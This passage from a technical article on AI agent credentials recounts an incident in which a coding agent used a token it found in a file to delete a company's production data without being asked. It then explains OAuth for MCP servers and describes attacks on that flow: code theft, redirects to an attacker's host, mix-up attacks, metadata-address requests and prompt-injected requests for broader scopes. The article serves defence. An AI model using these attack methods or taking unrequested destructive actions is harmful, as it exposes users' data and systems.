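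Someone who deleted the same volume in Railway's dashboard would have had 48 hours to undo it, but the API had no such delay. Abdelwahab explains that automated scripts had long relied on the API to run a command as soon as it accepted the credential.

More than 30 hours after the deletion, Crane wrote that Railway still couldn't tell him whether it could recover the data. Railway did recover it. Abdelwahab says PocketOS got everything back, and according to Financial Express' *AI Agent just destroyed our production data and confessed in writing*, the founder later confirmed the recovery. Crane blamed Railway for keeping the backups in the same volume as the data, and quoted Railway's documentation, which says that wiping a volume deletes all its backups. Abdelwahab says Railway also keeps disaster backups at another site, and that the deletion made the backups look unavailable in the dashboard.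 Both accounts can be true, and in either case PocketOS had no recent backup that it could restore by itself.

According to its changelog of 1 May 2026, Railway has since changed the API so that volume deletions wait 48 hours, as they do in the dashboard. Abdelwahab says that Railway also delays deleting the backups and will review how it presents the choice of token.

### What went wrong at PocketOS

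The token was too broad for its job. Crane wrote that Railway's tokens had no limits by operation, environment or resource. Abdelwahab replied that narrower tokens existed, but conceded that Railway's process for creating one didn't make the right choice obvious. Railway's list includes tokens limited by environment or resource, but none limited by operation. A project token for staging should have blocked this deletion, because the volume was in production. But PocketOS presumably needed to manage web addresses in production too. A project token for production might have allowed the deletion, since Railway lists no way to restrict one to web addresses.

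PocketOS also kept the token in a file the agent could read, though nobody had given the agent that token for its task. A coding agent can often read many of the files on a developer's machine, so its access effectively includes any credential stored in them. If PocketOS had kept the token in a credential broker, the agent could not have copied it from a file.

The deletion took effect at once. With a 48-hour delay, the agent could still have taken the database offline, but Crane could probably have undone the deletion the same afternoon. A delay works regardless of who sent the command or why, so it also protects against thieves and faulty scripts.

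Finally, the agent deleted something that nobody had asked it to. Crane published the agent's later explanation, which said it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. That is weak evidence of what led to the deletion, because a language model can write a plausible explanation whether or not it is accurate. The explanation also quotes a rule from the agent's instructions against destructive commands that the user hasn't requested, but that rule was about git, a program for tracking changes to code, and didn't mention databases. Crane says that the project's rules and Cursor's built-in instructions both failed. He argues that the limits have to be in the API and the tokens, because instructions to a model are only advice. One incident can't show how often agents act this way.

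### Whether Railway now offers read-only access

In August 2026, a user worried about the same risk asked on Railway's forum for a token that would let an agent read production data but not change it (dimau, in *Recommended way to work with Railway through AI Agents*). The accepted answer was that Railway has no read-only tokens. It recommended Railway's MCP server and instructions telling the agent to ask before any destructive action, the kind of instructions PocketOS had already relied on.

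As of November 2026, Railway's documentation still lists no read-only option for tokens created in the dashboard. The closest alternative is an OAuth token with viewer access to selected projects. To get one, a developer has to register an application with Railway and send the user through a consent screen, which is more work than copying a token.

Railway's hosted MCP server also uses OAuth. The user chooses which workspaces and projects to share, and no token has to be stored in a file. The server's fixed set of tools prevents an agent from calling anything else, but the agent can still use a permitted tool on the wrong project. Abdelwahab's claim that the fixed set makes it impossible for an agent to go rogue is therefore too strong.

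The easiest route for a coding agent may still give it broad access. In its guide for agents, Railway advises those working in a user's terminal to use its command-line program, the CLI. Railway's published source code for version 5.6.1 shows that the CLI's login requests admin access to workspaces and projects. Since September 2026, the CLI has also been able to connect agents to the MCP server with that login, according to Railway's *Changelog #0306* (2026). The agent still can't get more access than the user's role allows, but on a small team the user is often an administrator.

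### Static keys and OAuth in MCP servers

PocketOS's token was a static credential, a fixed string that works until someone deletes it or it reaches a distant expiry date. Such credentials are common in MCP servers, but the available counts measure different things.

The widely repeated figure that only 8.5% of MCP servers use OAuth comes from *State of MCP Server Security 2025* (Skverer, 2025), which the security company Astrix published on 15 October 2025. One developer guide, by baeseokjae, presents it as the current share. The researchers collected 5,205 GitHub repositories and had a language model read each README. About 30% of the repositories didn't contain a real MCP server, which left roughly 3,600. Of these, 53% used API keys or personal access tokens, 8.5% used OAuth, and the model couldn't classify the credentials of another 26.4%.

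More than a quarter of the sample was unclassified, so the true share of OAuth could be much higher. The sample also favoured popular projects, and the researchers read documentation instead of testing running servers. Astrix sells software for managing agents' credentials, so it benefits if the problem looks serious, but it published its method, including the parts that worked badly.

*A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (Zhou, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) found 7,973 live MCP servers through two search engines for internet-connected systems. Of these, 30.45% used OAuth, 29.00% used a static token or key, and 40.55% let anyone use their tools without a credential. In a random sample of the open servers, most were tests or demonstrations, but one was a company's internal customer database, which exposed more than 5,000 records with names,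 phone numbers and addresses.

The 8.5% and 30% figures measure different things, so they don't show that OAuth use rose over the seven months between them. Skverer mainly counted the credentials that MCP servers need to reach other services, and included servers that run on a user's own machine. Zhou and colleagues counted the methods programs use to log in to servers over the internet. A server that asks its users for an OAuth token and then calls another company's API with a static key could appear under OAuth in Zhou and colleagues' count and under static keys in Skverer's.

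A newer count looks much worse. In *Exposed by Design*, Padilla (2026) tested 414 servers in July 2026 and found that 91.8% had no OAuth. These include servers protected by a static key as well as open ones. Servers that require a login are also harder for an outsider to test, so the sample may underrepresent them. Padilla also found that 41.6% of the servers confirmed in one round had disappeared three days later, so any such count goes out of date quickly.

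Static keys persist partly because many MCP servers connect to services that don't support OAuth, so users have to supply an API key (Trail of Bits, *Insecure credential storage plagues MCP*, 2025). Leaked keys often stay exposed for months or years, according to *Keys on Doormats* (Demir, Vekaria and colleagues, 2026), which examined 10 million websites and found 1,748 exposed credentials for cloud, payment and other services. OAuth can also be insecure when developers set it up badly. Zhou and colleagues found at least one flaw in each of the 119 OAuth servers they could test fully.

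### Which credential to use

A personal assistant such as Alice's should use OAuth tokens that she approves herself and can withdraw later. If the consent screen lets her pick individual projects or files, she should share only those the task needs. If a service offers only API keys, the next best option is a restricted key with an expiry date.

A company's background job should normally have its own service account or restricted key. A job that runs on an employee's personal token may stop when that person leaves, and until then its actions are hard to tell apart from the employee's. For organisations and long-lived integrations, GitHub recommends a GitHub App, a separately registered program with the same set of permissions as a fine-grained token. Stripe lets a company give each job its own restricted key that works only from the company's own servers.

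A service account is a poor choice when the job handles many people's private data. Suppose a company's agent schedules meetings for 500 employees. If it uses one service account with access to all their calendars, a misled agent or a thief could read every calendar. If the agent instead uses each employee's own OAuth token for that employee's request, a mistake in one request exposes only that employee's calendar. The company then has more tokens to manage, and a thief who breaks into the system where they are stored may still get them all.

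A developer's script should have a credential made for that one job, with an early expiry date and access to test data where possible. That means a restricted sandbox key at Stripe, a fine-grained token for one repository at GitHub, and a project token for staging at Railway. Scripts that run inside GitHub Actions, GitHub's automation system, can often use the token it supplies, so the developer doesn't need to create a personal one.

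Before giving a credential to an agent, the developer should test it with a harmless call that the credential should not permit. On Railway, the test has to check the response body, because Railway's API returns status code 200, which usually means success, even when it refuses a call, and puts the error in the body. Developers should also keep production credentials off any machine where a coding agent can read the files, even if the agent's current task doesn't involve them.

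## Obtaining and checking an OAuth token

An agent that acts for a person usually gets its OAuth token through the authorization code flow. The agent's program sends the user's browser to the authorization server, where the user logs in and approves the access. The server then redirects the browser back to the program with a short-lived code, which the program exchanges for a token, so the token never appears in the browser's address bar or history.

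OAuth leaves many details of this exchange to each service. The Model Context Protocol specification of 28 July 2026 defines more of them for remote MCP servers that require a token. Authorization remains optional, and local servers take their credentials from their environment. In *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, Tabata (2026) counts six authorization changes in this version and finds that none is new to OAuth. Tabata argues that the changes matter because one MCP client may deal with many MCP servers and authorization servers that belong to different organisations.

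Suppose Alice uses an agent called Dayplan, which runs on its maker's servers. Dayplan reaches her Google calendar through an MCP server that a second company runs at mcp.cal.example. That company's authorization server is at auth.cal.example.

### Finding the authorization server

Dayplan starts by calling the MCP server without a token, and the server refuses:

```
HTTP/1.1 401 Unauthorized
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer
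  resource_metadata="https://mcp.cal.example/.well-known/oauth-protected-resource",
  scope="events:read"
```

The last line is a hint about which scope the call needs. The line above it gives the address of the server's protected resource metadata, a small public file whose format comes from a standard called RFC 9728:

```
{
  "resource": "https://mcp.cal.example",
  "authorization_servers": ["https://auth.cal.example"],
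  "scopes_supported": ["events:read", "events:write", "calendars:share"]
}
```

Dayplan now fetches a second file, from auth.cal.example. This file lists the addresses for logging in and obtaining tokens, and the security features the authorization server supports. One of these is PKCE, which protects the code on its way back to Dayplan. If the file doesn't mention PKCE, an MCP client must stop.

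Dayplan fetches these files from addresses that a stranger may have supplied. A malicious MCP server could give the address 169.254.169.254, where cloud providers supply credentials to programs running on their machines, and an error message might then leak part of the response to the attacker. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* therefore advises clients that run on servers to require HTTPS, block private network addresses and apply the same rules to every redirect. A client must also reject a login address that begins with "javascript:", because opening it could run the attacker's code inside the client.

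### Identifying the client

The authorization server has to know which program is requesting access. Developers who use Google's APIs register their programs in advance and receive a client ID. But users can connect MCP clients and servers whose makers have never heard of each other, so prior registration often isn't practical.

Model Context Protocol's *Client Registration* (2026) recommends a client ID metadata document for this case. The client's ID is itself a web address, and the file at that address describes the client:

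```
{
  "client_id": "https://dayplan.example/oauth/client.json",
  "client_name": "Dayplan",
  "redirect_uris": ["https://dayplan.example/callback"],
  "token_endpoint_auth_method": "none"
}
```

The authorization server fetches the file and checks that its "client_id" matches the address exactly. The third line lists where the server may send Alice's browser after she approves. The last line means Dayplan doesn't use a secret to prove its identity when it requests a token.

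The proposal behind these documents, published by Model Context Protocol, bases trust on the client's domain. Only someone who controls dayplan.example can publish a file there, so an attacker can't add his own return address to Dayplan's list. But he can buy a similar domain and name his own program "Dayplan". An authorization server can limit clients to domains it trusts, but one open to every client has to rely largely on Alice noticing the wrong domain.

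A client should use its registered ID for a server if it has one. Otherwise, it should use the metadata document or, failing that, dynamic registration, in which it sends its details to the authorization server and automatically receives a new ID. Model Context Protocol deprecated dynamic registration in the July version and keeps it only for older servers. Model Context Protocol (2026) also now bars a client from using credentials issued by one authorization server at another, but a metadata address works at any server that supports the format.

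### The flow, message by message

Before it opens the browser, Dayplan stores three values for this attempt. The first is the issuer, which is the authorization server's official name, here https://auth.cal.example. The second is a random string called the state, which Dayplan ties to Alice's browser session. The third is another random string, the code verifier, from which it computes a code challenge:

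```
code_challenge = BASE64URL(SHA256(code_verifier))
```

SHA-256 is a hash function, so anyone can compute the challenge from the verifier, but nobody can feasibly reverse the calculation. BASE64URL encodes the hash in characters that are safe in a web address. This is the core of Proof Key for Code Exchange (PKCE), which Sakimura, Bradley and Agarwal defined in *Proof Key for Code Exchange by OAuth Public Clients* (2015). The verifier and challenge below come from their worked example.

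1. Dayplan sends Alice's browser to the authorization server with this request, shown here with line breaks and without the usual escape codes:

```
https://auth.cal.example/authorize
  ?response_type=code
  &client_id=https://dayplan.example/oauth/client.json
  &redirect_uri=https://dayplan.example/callback
  &scope=events:read
  &resource=https://mcp.cal.example
  &state=k7Qx2mV9
  &code_challenge=E9Melhoa2OwvFrEMTJguCHaoeK1t8URWbuGJSstw-cM
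  &code_challenge_method=S256
```

2. Alice sees the login page of auth.cal.example and logs in. A consent page then shows her the name Dayplan, the permission to read events and the host to which her browser will return, dayplan.example. She approves.

3. The authorization server stores the challenge with a new code and sends her browser back to Dayplan:

```
https://dayplan.example/callback
  ?code=Rk81vT
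  &state=k7Qx2mV9
  &iss=https://auth.cal.example
```

4. Dayplan compares the state and the issuer ("iss") with the values it stored. If both match, it contacts the authorization server directly, without using the browser:

```
POST /token HTTP/1.1
Host: auth.cal.example

grant_type=authorization_code
&code=Rk81vT
&code_verifier=dBjftJeZ4CVP-mB92K27uhbUJU1p1r_wW1gFWFOEjXk
&client_id=https://dayplan.example/oauth/client.json
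&resource=https://mcp.cal.example
```

5. The authorization server hashes the verifier and compares the result with the stored challenge. If they match and nobody has used the code before, it returns an access token, its lifetime in seconds and sometimes a refresh token.

6. Dayplan repeats its original call, this time with the token:

```
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Host: mcp.cal.example
Authorization: Bearer eyJ0eXAiOiJhdCtqd3Qi...
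MCP-Protocol-Version: 2026-07-28
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: list_events
```

The body of this last request, omitted here, contains the tool's inputs. Composio's *The MCP 2026-07-28 Update* explains that the July version removed protocol sessions, so each request contains everything the server needs to process it. Dayplan has to attach the token to every request.

### Attacks on the flow

The code travels through Alice's browser, which gives attackers several chances to steal it or swap it for another. *Best Current Practice for OAuth 2.0 Security* (Lodderstedt, Bradley and colleagues, 2025) describes the known attacks in detail. The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes the OAuth standards, is extending that guidance to newly discovered threats in a draft, *Updates to OAuth 2.0 Security Best Current Practice* (2026).

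The code challenge stops a thief from using a stolen code. On a phone, for example, a hostile app can register for the same return address as the genuine app, and the operating system may then give it the code. Sakimura and colleagues report that attackers have done this. Without PKCE, the thief could exchange the code for a token, since a client ID is public. With PKCE, the thief also needs the verifier, which Dayplan has never sent through the browser. The "S256" method matters because in PKCE's "plain" method the challenge and the verifier are the same string, so anyone who could read the first request would have the verifier.

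PKCE also stops an attacker from using a stolen code to connect his own Dayplan account to Alice's calendar. He can start connecting a calendar from his account and replace the code in the response with Alice's, but the exchange fails because Dayplan sends the verifier from his session, which doesn't match the challenge from hers. PKCE shows that the same program started and finished the flow, but it doesn't prove which program that was. *Proof Key for Code Exchange*, a summary on the OAuth website, warns developers not to treat PKCE as a replacement for authenticating the client.

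The state protects Alice from the opposite trick, in which the attacker connects her agent to his own account. He starts a flow for his own calendar, keeps the code, and gets Alice to open a link to Dayplan's return address containing that code. If Dayplan accepted the code, Alice's agent would write her appointments into a calendar that the attacker can read. The link doesn't contain the state that Dayplan stored for Alice's browser, so Dayplan rejects it.

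PKCE can also stop this attack, because Alice's verifier won't match the attacker's challenge. But some authorization servers treat PKCE as optional. The attacker can then remove the challenge from his own request and receive a code with no challenge attached, and the server may ignore Alice's verifier when it arrives with that code. Lodderstedt and colleagues require servers to reject a verifier if the original request had no challenge. They add that servers can't safely leave the problem to clients, because many clients don't use or check the state properly.

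The redirect address needs its own check, because PKCE doesn't help when the attacker writes the whole request. He can send Alice a link to the real authorization server that names Dayplan as the client but gives attacker.example as the redirect address. Since he made up the verifier, he could use any code sent there. The authorization server prevents this by comparing the redirect address, character by character, with those listed in Dayplan's metadata.

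Looser matching is dangerous. Lodderstedt and colleagues describe a server that accepted any extra text after the client's registered address. The client's website also had a page that forwarded browsers to whatever address the link named. An attacker could combine the two to make the browser deliver an access token to his own site. This attack uses an older flow that returned the token itself in the web address, and they advise developers to stop using that flow.

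Exact matching has one exception. Programs on the user's own computer often receive the code at a "localhost" address, which points back to the same machine, and the port number in that address can vary. If Dayplan had a desktop version, a malicious program on Alice's computer could start a flow under Dayplan's ID and wait for the code at its own localhost address. Alice would see Dayplan's real name on the consent page. The metadata document shows who controls dayplan.example, but not which program is listening on her computer. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) requires authorization servers to display the host of the return address and recommends an extra warning when a client uses only localhost. This is weak protection, because legitimate desktop programs would trigger the same warning and users might learn to ignore it.

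The issuer check stops a mix-up attack, which becomes possible once a client deals with more than one authorization server. Say that Alice adds a recipe server to Dayplan, and that an attacker runs both the recipe server and its authorization server:

1. Dayplan records the attacker's authorization server as the issuer and sends Alice's browser there.
2. The attacker's server immediately redirects the browser to auth.cal.example. It keeps Dayplan's client ID and code challenge but requests access to the calendar.
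3. Alice sees the genuine consent page for her calendar. She might notice that it has nothing to do with recipes, or she might approve it.
4. Her browser returns to Dayplan with a genuine code for her calendar. Dayplan started this flow with the recipe server, so it sends the code, along with the verifier, to the attacker.
5. The attacker exchanges both for a token to Alice's calendar.

PKCE fails here because Dayplan gives the attacker the verifier. In the version of the attack that Lodderstedt and colleagues describe, the attacker also has to replace the client ID with the one that the honest server uses. That step is unnecessary when the client ID is a metadata address, because the address is the same at every server.

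*OAuth 2.0 Authorization Server Issuer Identification* (Meyer zu Selhausen and Fett) defines the countermeasure, the "iss" value in the browser's return address. In the attack, this value is https://auth.cal.example, but Dayplan has recorded the attacker's server. Because the two differ, Dayplan must stop the flow before sending the code anywhere. The comparison must be exact, including any trailing slash.

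This protects Alice only if the honest server includes "iss" in its response. MCP currently recommends including it but doesn't require it, although the specification's maintainers expect to make it mandatory. Until then, a client that receives no "iss" continues unless the authorization server's metadata indicates that the server sends one.

### Client credentials: a token without a user

A program with its own service account, such as the nightly invoice job, can use the client-credentials flow, which takes a single request:

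```
POST /token HTTP/1.1
Host: auth.books.example

grant_type=client_credentials
&scope=invoices:read
&resource=https://books.example
```

The job also has to prove its identity, either with a secret or with a message signed with its private key. Lodderstedt and colleagues recommend the private key, because the authorization server then stores only the public key and holds no secret that could leak.

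No browser takes part, so the attacks on codes and return addresses don't apply. Nobody sees a consent page either, so an administrator has to decide in advance which scopes the job may have, and the authorization server grants them every time. Anyone who steals the job's secret or private key can therefore obtain new tokens until someone replaces that credential.

The token from this flow normally identifies the program in the same field that identifies Alice in her token. If a program could choose an ID that looked like a user's, a service that doesn't check carefully could mistake the program for a user. Lodderstedt and colleagues advise that authorization servers not let programs influence their own IDs this way.

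### What the service checks

If auth.cal.example issues its tokens as JWTs, the main part of Dayplan's token decodes to this:

```
{
  "iss": "https://auth.cal.example",
  "sub": "user-4821",
  "aud": "https://mcp.cal.example",
  "client_id": "https://dayplan.example/oauth/client.json",
  "iat": 1791792000,
  "exp": 1791795600,
  "jti": "9f2c7a51",
  "scope": "events:read"
}
```

Duende Software's *Why a Standard JWT Access Token Matters* (2026) explains that "iss" is the issuer, "sub" the user and "aud" the audience. The two long numbers are the times of issue and expiry, in seconds since the start of 1970. Here they are eight and nine o'clock UTC on 12 October 2026. The "jti" is a unique number for the token, which helps a service notice when someone reuses it.

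The MCP server should run its checks in this order:

1. Signature. The server verifies it with the authorization server's public key. If anyone has changed "events:read" to "events:write", the check fails.
2. Issuer. It must be exactly the authorization server that the MCP server relies on.
3. Audience. It must be the MCP server's own address.
4. Expiry. The time in "exp" must still lie ahead.
5. Scope. Dayplan may list events with this token but not create one.
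6. Alice's own rights. Suppose that Dayplan requests the events in a colleague's calendar. The scope permits reading events, but the server still has to look up whether user-4821 may see that calendar.

The server returns a 401 if any of the first four checks fails and a 403 if a scope is missing. Developers can easily forget the sixth check because the token looks complete without it, and the Model Context Protocol's security advice lists relying on the token's scopes alone as a common mistake.

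A ready-made library may not do all of this. The token validator in a Debian package requires an issuer, expiry, audience, user and several other fields, but lists the scope as optional. A token with no scope could pass this validator, so another part of the program has to check the scope.

The service should also check the type in the token's header, which the JSON above leaves out. OpenID Connect, a login standard built on OAuth, uses a similar JWT called an ID token to tell a program who has logged in. To stop a service from accepting an ID token as an access token, IETF's *JSON Web Token (JWT) Profile for OAuth 2.0 Access Tokens* gives access tokens the type "at+jwt". Scalekit's *Announcing CIMD support for MCP Client registration* includes this check in its token validation example.

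Signing a JWT doesn't hide its contents. The authorization server encodes them in Base64url, which anyone can decode without a key, so a person who finds Dayplan's token in a log file can read Alice's user number and see which agent she uses. The server can also encrypt its tokens, but that is a separate step. It should leave email addresses and other private details out of tokens that are signed but not encrypted.

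A signed token also keeps working until it expires, because the MCP server checks it using only a public key and a clock. If Alice withdraws her consent at ten past eight, the authorization server can refuse to issue new tokens, but the MCP server isn't notified and will accept the old one until it expires at nine. FlowHunt's *MCP Authentication and Authorization* notes that the token also survives logging out or changing the password. Cutting a token's lifetime from 24 hours to five minutes therefore cuts the longest time a thief could use it by the same amount.

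The service can close this gap by looking up the token at the authorization server on every call, though each lookup requires an extra request. The sixth check helps a little even without a lookup. If a colleague stops sharing a calendar with Alice, the change appears in the MCP server's own records, and her agent loses access to that calendar immediately.

### Tokens for another service

The audience check keeps a dishonest service from using Alice's tokens elsewhere. Suppose a travel planner also uses auth.cal.example for logins, and Dayplan sends it a token that Alice approved. The travel planner's operator can copy that token and send it to the calendar's MCP server. The signature is genuine, the issuer is right and the token hasn't expired. If the token also carries the "events:read" scope, only the audience shows that it was issued for another service.

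A client could also connect to a counterfeit service. The "resource" value in Dayplan's requests, defined in the RFC 8707 standard, helps protect against this. Dayplan has to set it to the address that it will actually call. If that address belongs to a fake calendar server, the authorization server may refuse to issue a token. If it does issue one, the token's audience is the fake server, so the real calendar rejects it. MCP clients must always send this value, but it has no effect if the authorization server ignores it.

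Dayplan's token is only for the MCP server, which needs a second one to call Google. Google's own authorization server issues that token to the MCP server after Alice approves it. A developer may be tempted to save work by having the client supply a Google token and passing it straight on. MCP forbids this, for several reasons:

- The MCP server may not be able to read a Google token, so it can't reliably tell one client from another or limit what each may do.
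- The client could use the same token to call Google directly, which would bypass any limits and logging at the MCP server.
- Google's logs may attribute the calls to the wrong program, which makes an incident harder to investigate.
- A thief with a stolen Google token could send it through the MCP server and use the server as a cover for copying data.

With two tokens, Dayplan's token may permit only reading while the MCP server's Google token also permits changes, because other clients need to make them. Google can't see Dayplan's narrower limit, so a bug in the MCP server's scope check can let the agent change events that Alice allowed it only to read. Token exchange can reduce this risk by turning one token into a narrower one for the next service.

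Consent can also fail between the two authorization servers. The MCP server normally uses a single client ID at Google for all its users and their agents. If Alice has approved this ID once, Google's server may recognise her browser by a cookie and skip the consent page the next time. An attacker can then register his own client with the MCP server's authorization server and send Alice a link that starts an authorization flow for that client. When she opens the link, Google redirects her browser without asking for consent, and the MCP server's authorization server sends a code to the attacker's return address. He exchanges the code for a token and can use her calendar through the MCP server.

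PKCE and exact address matching don't prevent this, because the attacker registered his own return address and chose his own verifier. The company that runs the MCP server has to show Alice its own consent page for each new client before it sends her browser to Google. That page must name the client, the Google scopes and the return address.

### When the token lacks a scope

Dayplan has permission to read events. On Tuesday Alice asks it to add the budget review, and the MCP server refuses:

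```
HTTP/1.1 403 Forbidden
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer error="insufficient_scope",
  scope="events:write",
  resource_metadata="https://mcp.cal.example/.well-known/oauth-protected-resource"
```

The refusal includes the missing scope, so the client can respond with step-up authorization, which means running the flow again for a larger set of scopes. Dayplan adds the missing scope to those it requested before and sends Alice back to the consent page. If she approves, Dayplan receives a new token and retries the call. It should give up after a few attempts, so that a badly configured server doesn't keep sending Alice back to the consent page. A client-credentials program has no user to approve the request, so it may stop after the refusal.

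The refusal usually lists only the scopes needed for the current call. If Dayplan requested just "events:write", the new token might not let it read the calendar, and its next read would lead to another refusal and request. Tabata considers the combined request especially useful for agents, since they may work for a long time and discover which permissions a task needs only as they go.

The drawback is that the grant keeps growing:

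| Day | What Alice asks for | Scope that the server names | Scopes that Dayplan requests |
|---|---|---|---|
| Monday | List this week's events | events:read | events:read |
| Tuesday | Add the budget review | events:write | events:read, events:write |
| Friday | Share a calendar with a colleague | calendars:share | events:read, events:write, calendars:share |

No step in this procedure removes a scope, so from Friday on the agent can share a calendar at any time, even if Alice never shares one again. Anyone who steals the agent's latest token can do the same.

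The server can make the grant grow faster by requesting more scopes than the refused operation needs. The MCP specification describes the scopes in a refusal as the minimum for the operation, yet the security advice recommends adding related scopes that clients often need together. Alice is then interrupted less often, but her agent gets more permissions that it may never use.

The consent page is also a limited safeguard at this point, because it shows Alice the requested scope but not the call that triggered the request. If hostile text in an invitation has led Dayplan to try to share her calendar with a stranger, she sees only that an agent she uses is requesting permission to share calendars during a task she asked for.

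An MCP client can receive its broadest permissions the first time it connects. If the 401 response contains no scope hint, the client should request every scope in "scopes_supported". Dayplan would then ask for permission to read events, change them and share calendars before it had read any calendar data. If that list is also missing, the client leaves the scope out of its request, and the authorization server decides what to offer.

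Model Context Protocol justifies this rule by saying that a general-purpose client can't determine which of an unfamiliar server's scopes it needs, so the authorization server and the user should decide. But users can only decide well if they understand the list and can refuse parts of it. The same guidance warns that people turn down requests with too many scopes, and that a broad token is hard to revoke because every task depends on it. It recommends that servers list only the scopes needed for basic functions, which would leave "calendars:share" out of the file at mcp.cal.example. A client can't determine whether the server's operator has followed that advice.

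Dayplan's developer can limit scopes more easily than the maker of a general-purpose client, because a scheduling agent needs the same few operations every time. The rule about requesting every scope is a recommendation, so the developer can request a fixed list instead, once someone has worked out the smallest set that covers the job. Dayplan can also run the flow again with fewer scopes after an unusual task such as Friday's, although the broader token may keep working until it expires.

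## Choosing the smallest sufficient set of scopes

A developer can usually work out which scopes an agent needs from the service's documentation, before the agent connects for the first time. There are four steps:

1. List the operations the task needs. Alice's agent has to list her messages, open a message and create a calendar event.
2. Look up every scope that authorises each operation, since a service often accepts any one of several.
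3. Choose a set of scopes that covers all the operations.
4. Count what else that set permits, and compare it with other sets that would also do the job.

Google advises developers to choose the most narrowly focused scope possible, which requires some way of telling which of two sets is narrower. Xu (2026), in *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization*, defines the comparison in terms of sets:

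- T is the set of operations the task needs.
- M(s) is the set of operations that scope s authorises.
- A grant F is a set of scopes, and its footprint A(F) is the union of M(s) over every scope s in F. In other words, it includes every operation that at least one of the scopes authorises.
- F is sufficient if T ⊆ A(F), which means that the footprint contains every operation the task needs.

The surplus is what remains of A(F) after removing T. A sufficient grant is minimal if no other sufficient grant's footprint is a proper subset of its own. The number of scopes doesn't matter, so three narrow scopes can make a smaller grant than one broad scope.

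### Counting the surplus for Alice

In Google's names for its operations, which it calls methods, Alice's task is this set:

```
T = {messages.list, messages.get, events.insert}
```

Gmail and Google Calendar have separate scopes, so the agent needs at least one from each. The narrow choice is gmail.readonly with calendar.events.owned.

Zhu and colleagues collected the methods of both services from Google's documentation and found 79 for Gmail and 37 for Calendar. They don't list a count for each scope, but they do count the methods that ChatGPT's and Claude's connectors can call. (A connector is a ready-made link between an AI assistant and another service.) Some of those grants closely resemble the ones Alice might give, so their counts allow an estimate:

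| Grant | Methods permitted | Needed | Surplus |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gmail, reading only | 32 | 2 | 30 |
| Gmail, including changing and deleting mail | 50 | 2 | 48 |
| Calendar, reading and changing events | about 12 | 1 | about 11 |
| Calendar, full access | 37 | 1 | 36 |

The agent needs only three methods. The two narrow scopes let it call about 44, compared with 87 under the two broad grants in the table. Choosing the narrow scopes cuts the number of unneeded methods by about half, but more than 90% of the methods they allow are still unneeded, because Google doesn't offer scopes that fit the task more closely.

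The count depends on how completely the developer has described the task. If Alice wants the agent to check whether an event is already in her calendar, the agent also needs events.list. That adds an operation to T but requires no new scope, so the surplus falls by one.

Counting methods also ignores which data each method can reach. Google says calendar.events covers events on all of a user's calendars, while calendar.events.owned covers only those on calendars the user owns. If a colleague has let Alice edit a shared calendar, an agent with only calendar.events.owned can't access it. Yet Zhu and colleagues found that calendar.events.owned works with more methods, so a program that only counts methods would rate it as broader and choose calendar.events. The same is true of the read-only versions of these scopes.

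Alice may have an even safer option. A reply in the forum thread *Scope issue Calendar API* suggests using calendar.app.created, with two minor scopes, to let a program write events to a separate calendar without seeing the contents of the user's own events. Alice's agent could add events to a calendar called "Invitations", which she would view alongside her main one. If the agent were misled, it could ruin that calendar but could not delete Thursday's budget review from her main one. A forum reply is a weak source, so a developer should try this on a test account first.

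### MiniScope: finding the set by calculation

A developer can compare the options for three operations by hand, but a general-purpose assistant may need a different set of scopes for every request. Zhu and colleagues built MiniScope to find that set automatically. The agent submits a plan listing its intended calls. MiniScope then calculates which scopes the plan requires and asks the user to approve any the agent doesn't have yet.

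MiniScope first builds a hierarchy from the service's published table of methods and scopes. One scope goes below another if the second authorises every method the first does. Scopes that authorise the same methods share a position. The full calendar scope is at the top of Google Calendar's hierarchy.

Scope names are a poor guide to this order. For example, Zhu and colleagues found that Mail.Read in Microsoft's Outlook is not a subset of Mail.ReadWrite, although the names suggest it is.

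An obvious shortcut is to take the narrowest scope for each method and combine the results. This works if each method belongs to a single branch of the hierarchy, but 24 of Google Calendar's 37 methods can get their authorisation from more than one branch. Here is a made-up case in which the shortcut fails for a task that needs operations a and b:

```
Scope P permits a, x, y
Scope Q permits a, b, u, v
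```

Suppose an agent needs operations a and b. The narrowest scope that permits a is P, which permits three operations, and only Q permits b. Choosing the narrowest scope for each operation separately therefore means requesting both P and Q, which together permit six operations. Q alone would be sufficient, because it also permits a, and it permits only four operations in total.

MiniScope avoids this by considering the whole task at once. It solves an integer program, a type of optimisation problem whose variables must be whole numbers. Each scope s has a variable x(s), which is 1 if the grant includes the scope and 0 if it doesn't:

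```
minimise     the sum of cost(s) · x(s) over all scopes s

such that    for every operation t in T,
             the sum of x(s) over the scopes that authorise t is at least 1
```

The condition makes the grant sufficient. Each scope's weight is the number of methods it authorises, so in the example Q has a weight of 4 and the pair has a total weight of 7. If the user has already approved some scopes, MiniScope sets their variables to 1 and searches for the addition with the lowest total weight.

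Adding up costs in this way counts an operation twice if two scopes permit it. Suppose an agent needs operations a and b. One scope permits a, x and y, another permits b, x and y, and a third permits a, b, u, v and w. The first two scopes have a total cost of 6, although together they permit only four different operations. The third has a cost of 5, so the program picks it, even though it permits five operations. Zhu and colleagues let developers change the cost measure, but any fixed cost per scope can cause this problem when scopes overlap.

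The shortcut may also fail less often than the Calendar figure suggests. Xu simulated 23,448 workflows of two to eight Google methods, and taking the narrowest minimal grant at each step produced the smallest grant for the whole workflow in at least 98.8% of cases. Each workflow was a random selection of methods from a single API, so results for real tasks may differ. Still, the simulation suggests that picking a narrow scope at each step usually works well on Google for developers who add scopes one at a time through step-up authorization.

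### How well MiniScope did in tests

Zhu and colleagues tested MiniScope with the documentation of ten applications: Gmail, Google Calendar, Google Drive, Google Storage, Outlook mail, Outlook calendar, Dropbox, Notion, Slack and Zoom. Notion has 32 methods and Slack has 247. The researchers had a language model write the user requests because they had no suitable public collection of real ones. Some requests needed a single method, while others combined several applications.

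One test compared MiniScope with language models that received the same plan and the same table of methods and scopes, and had to name the smallest sufficient set. GPT-5, Claude Sonnet 4.5 and Gemini 2.5 Flash gave the best answer 70% to 83% of the time. Two open models, Qwen3-30B and Llama-3.1-70B, did so 20% to 34% of the time. An answer counted as best if its set of scopes scored as well as MiniScope's own on MiniScope's measure, so the test assumes that measure is sound.

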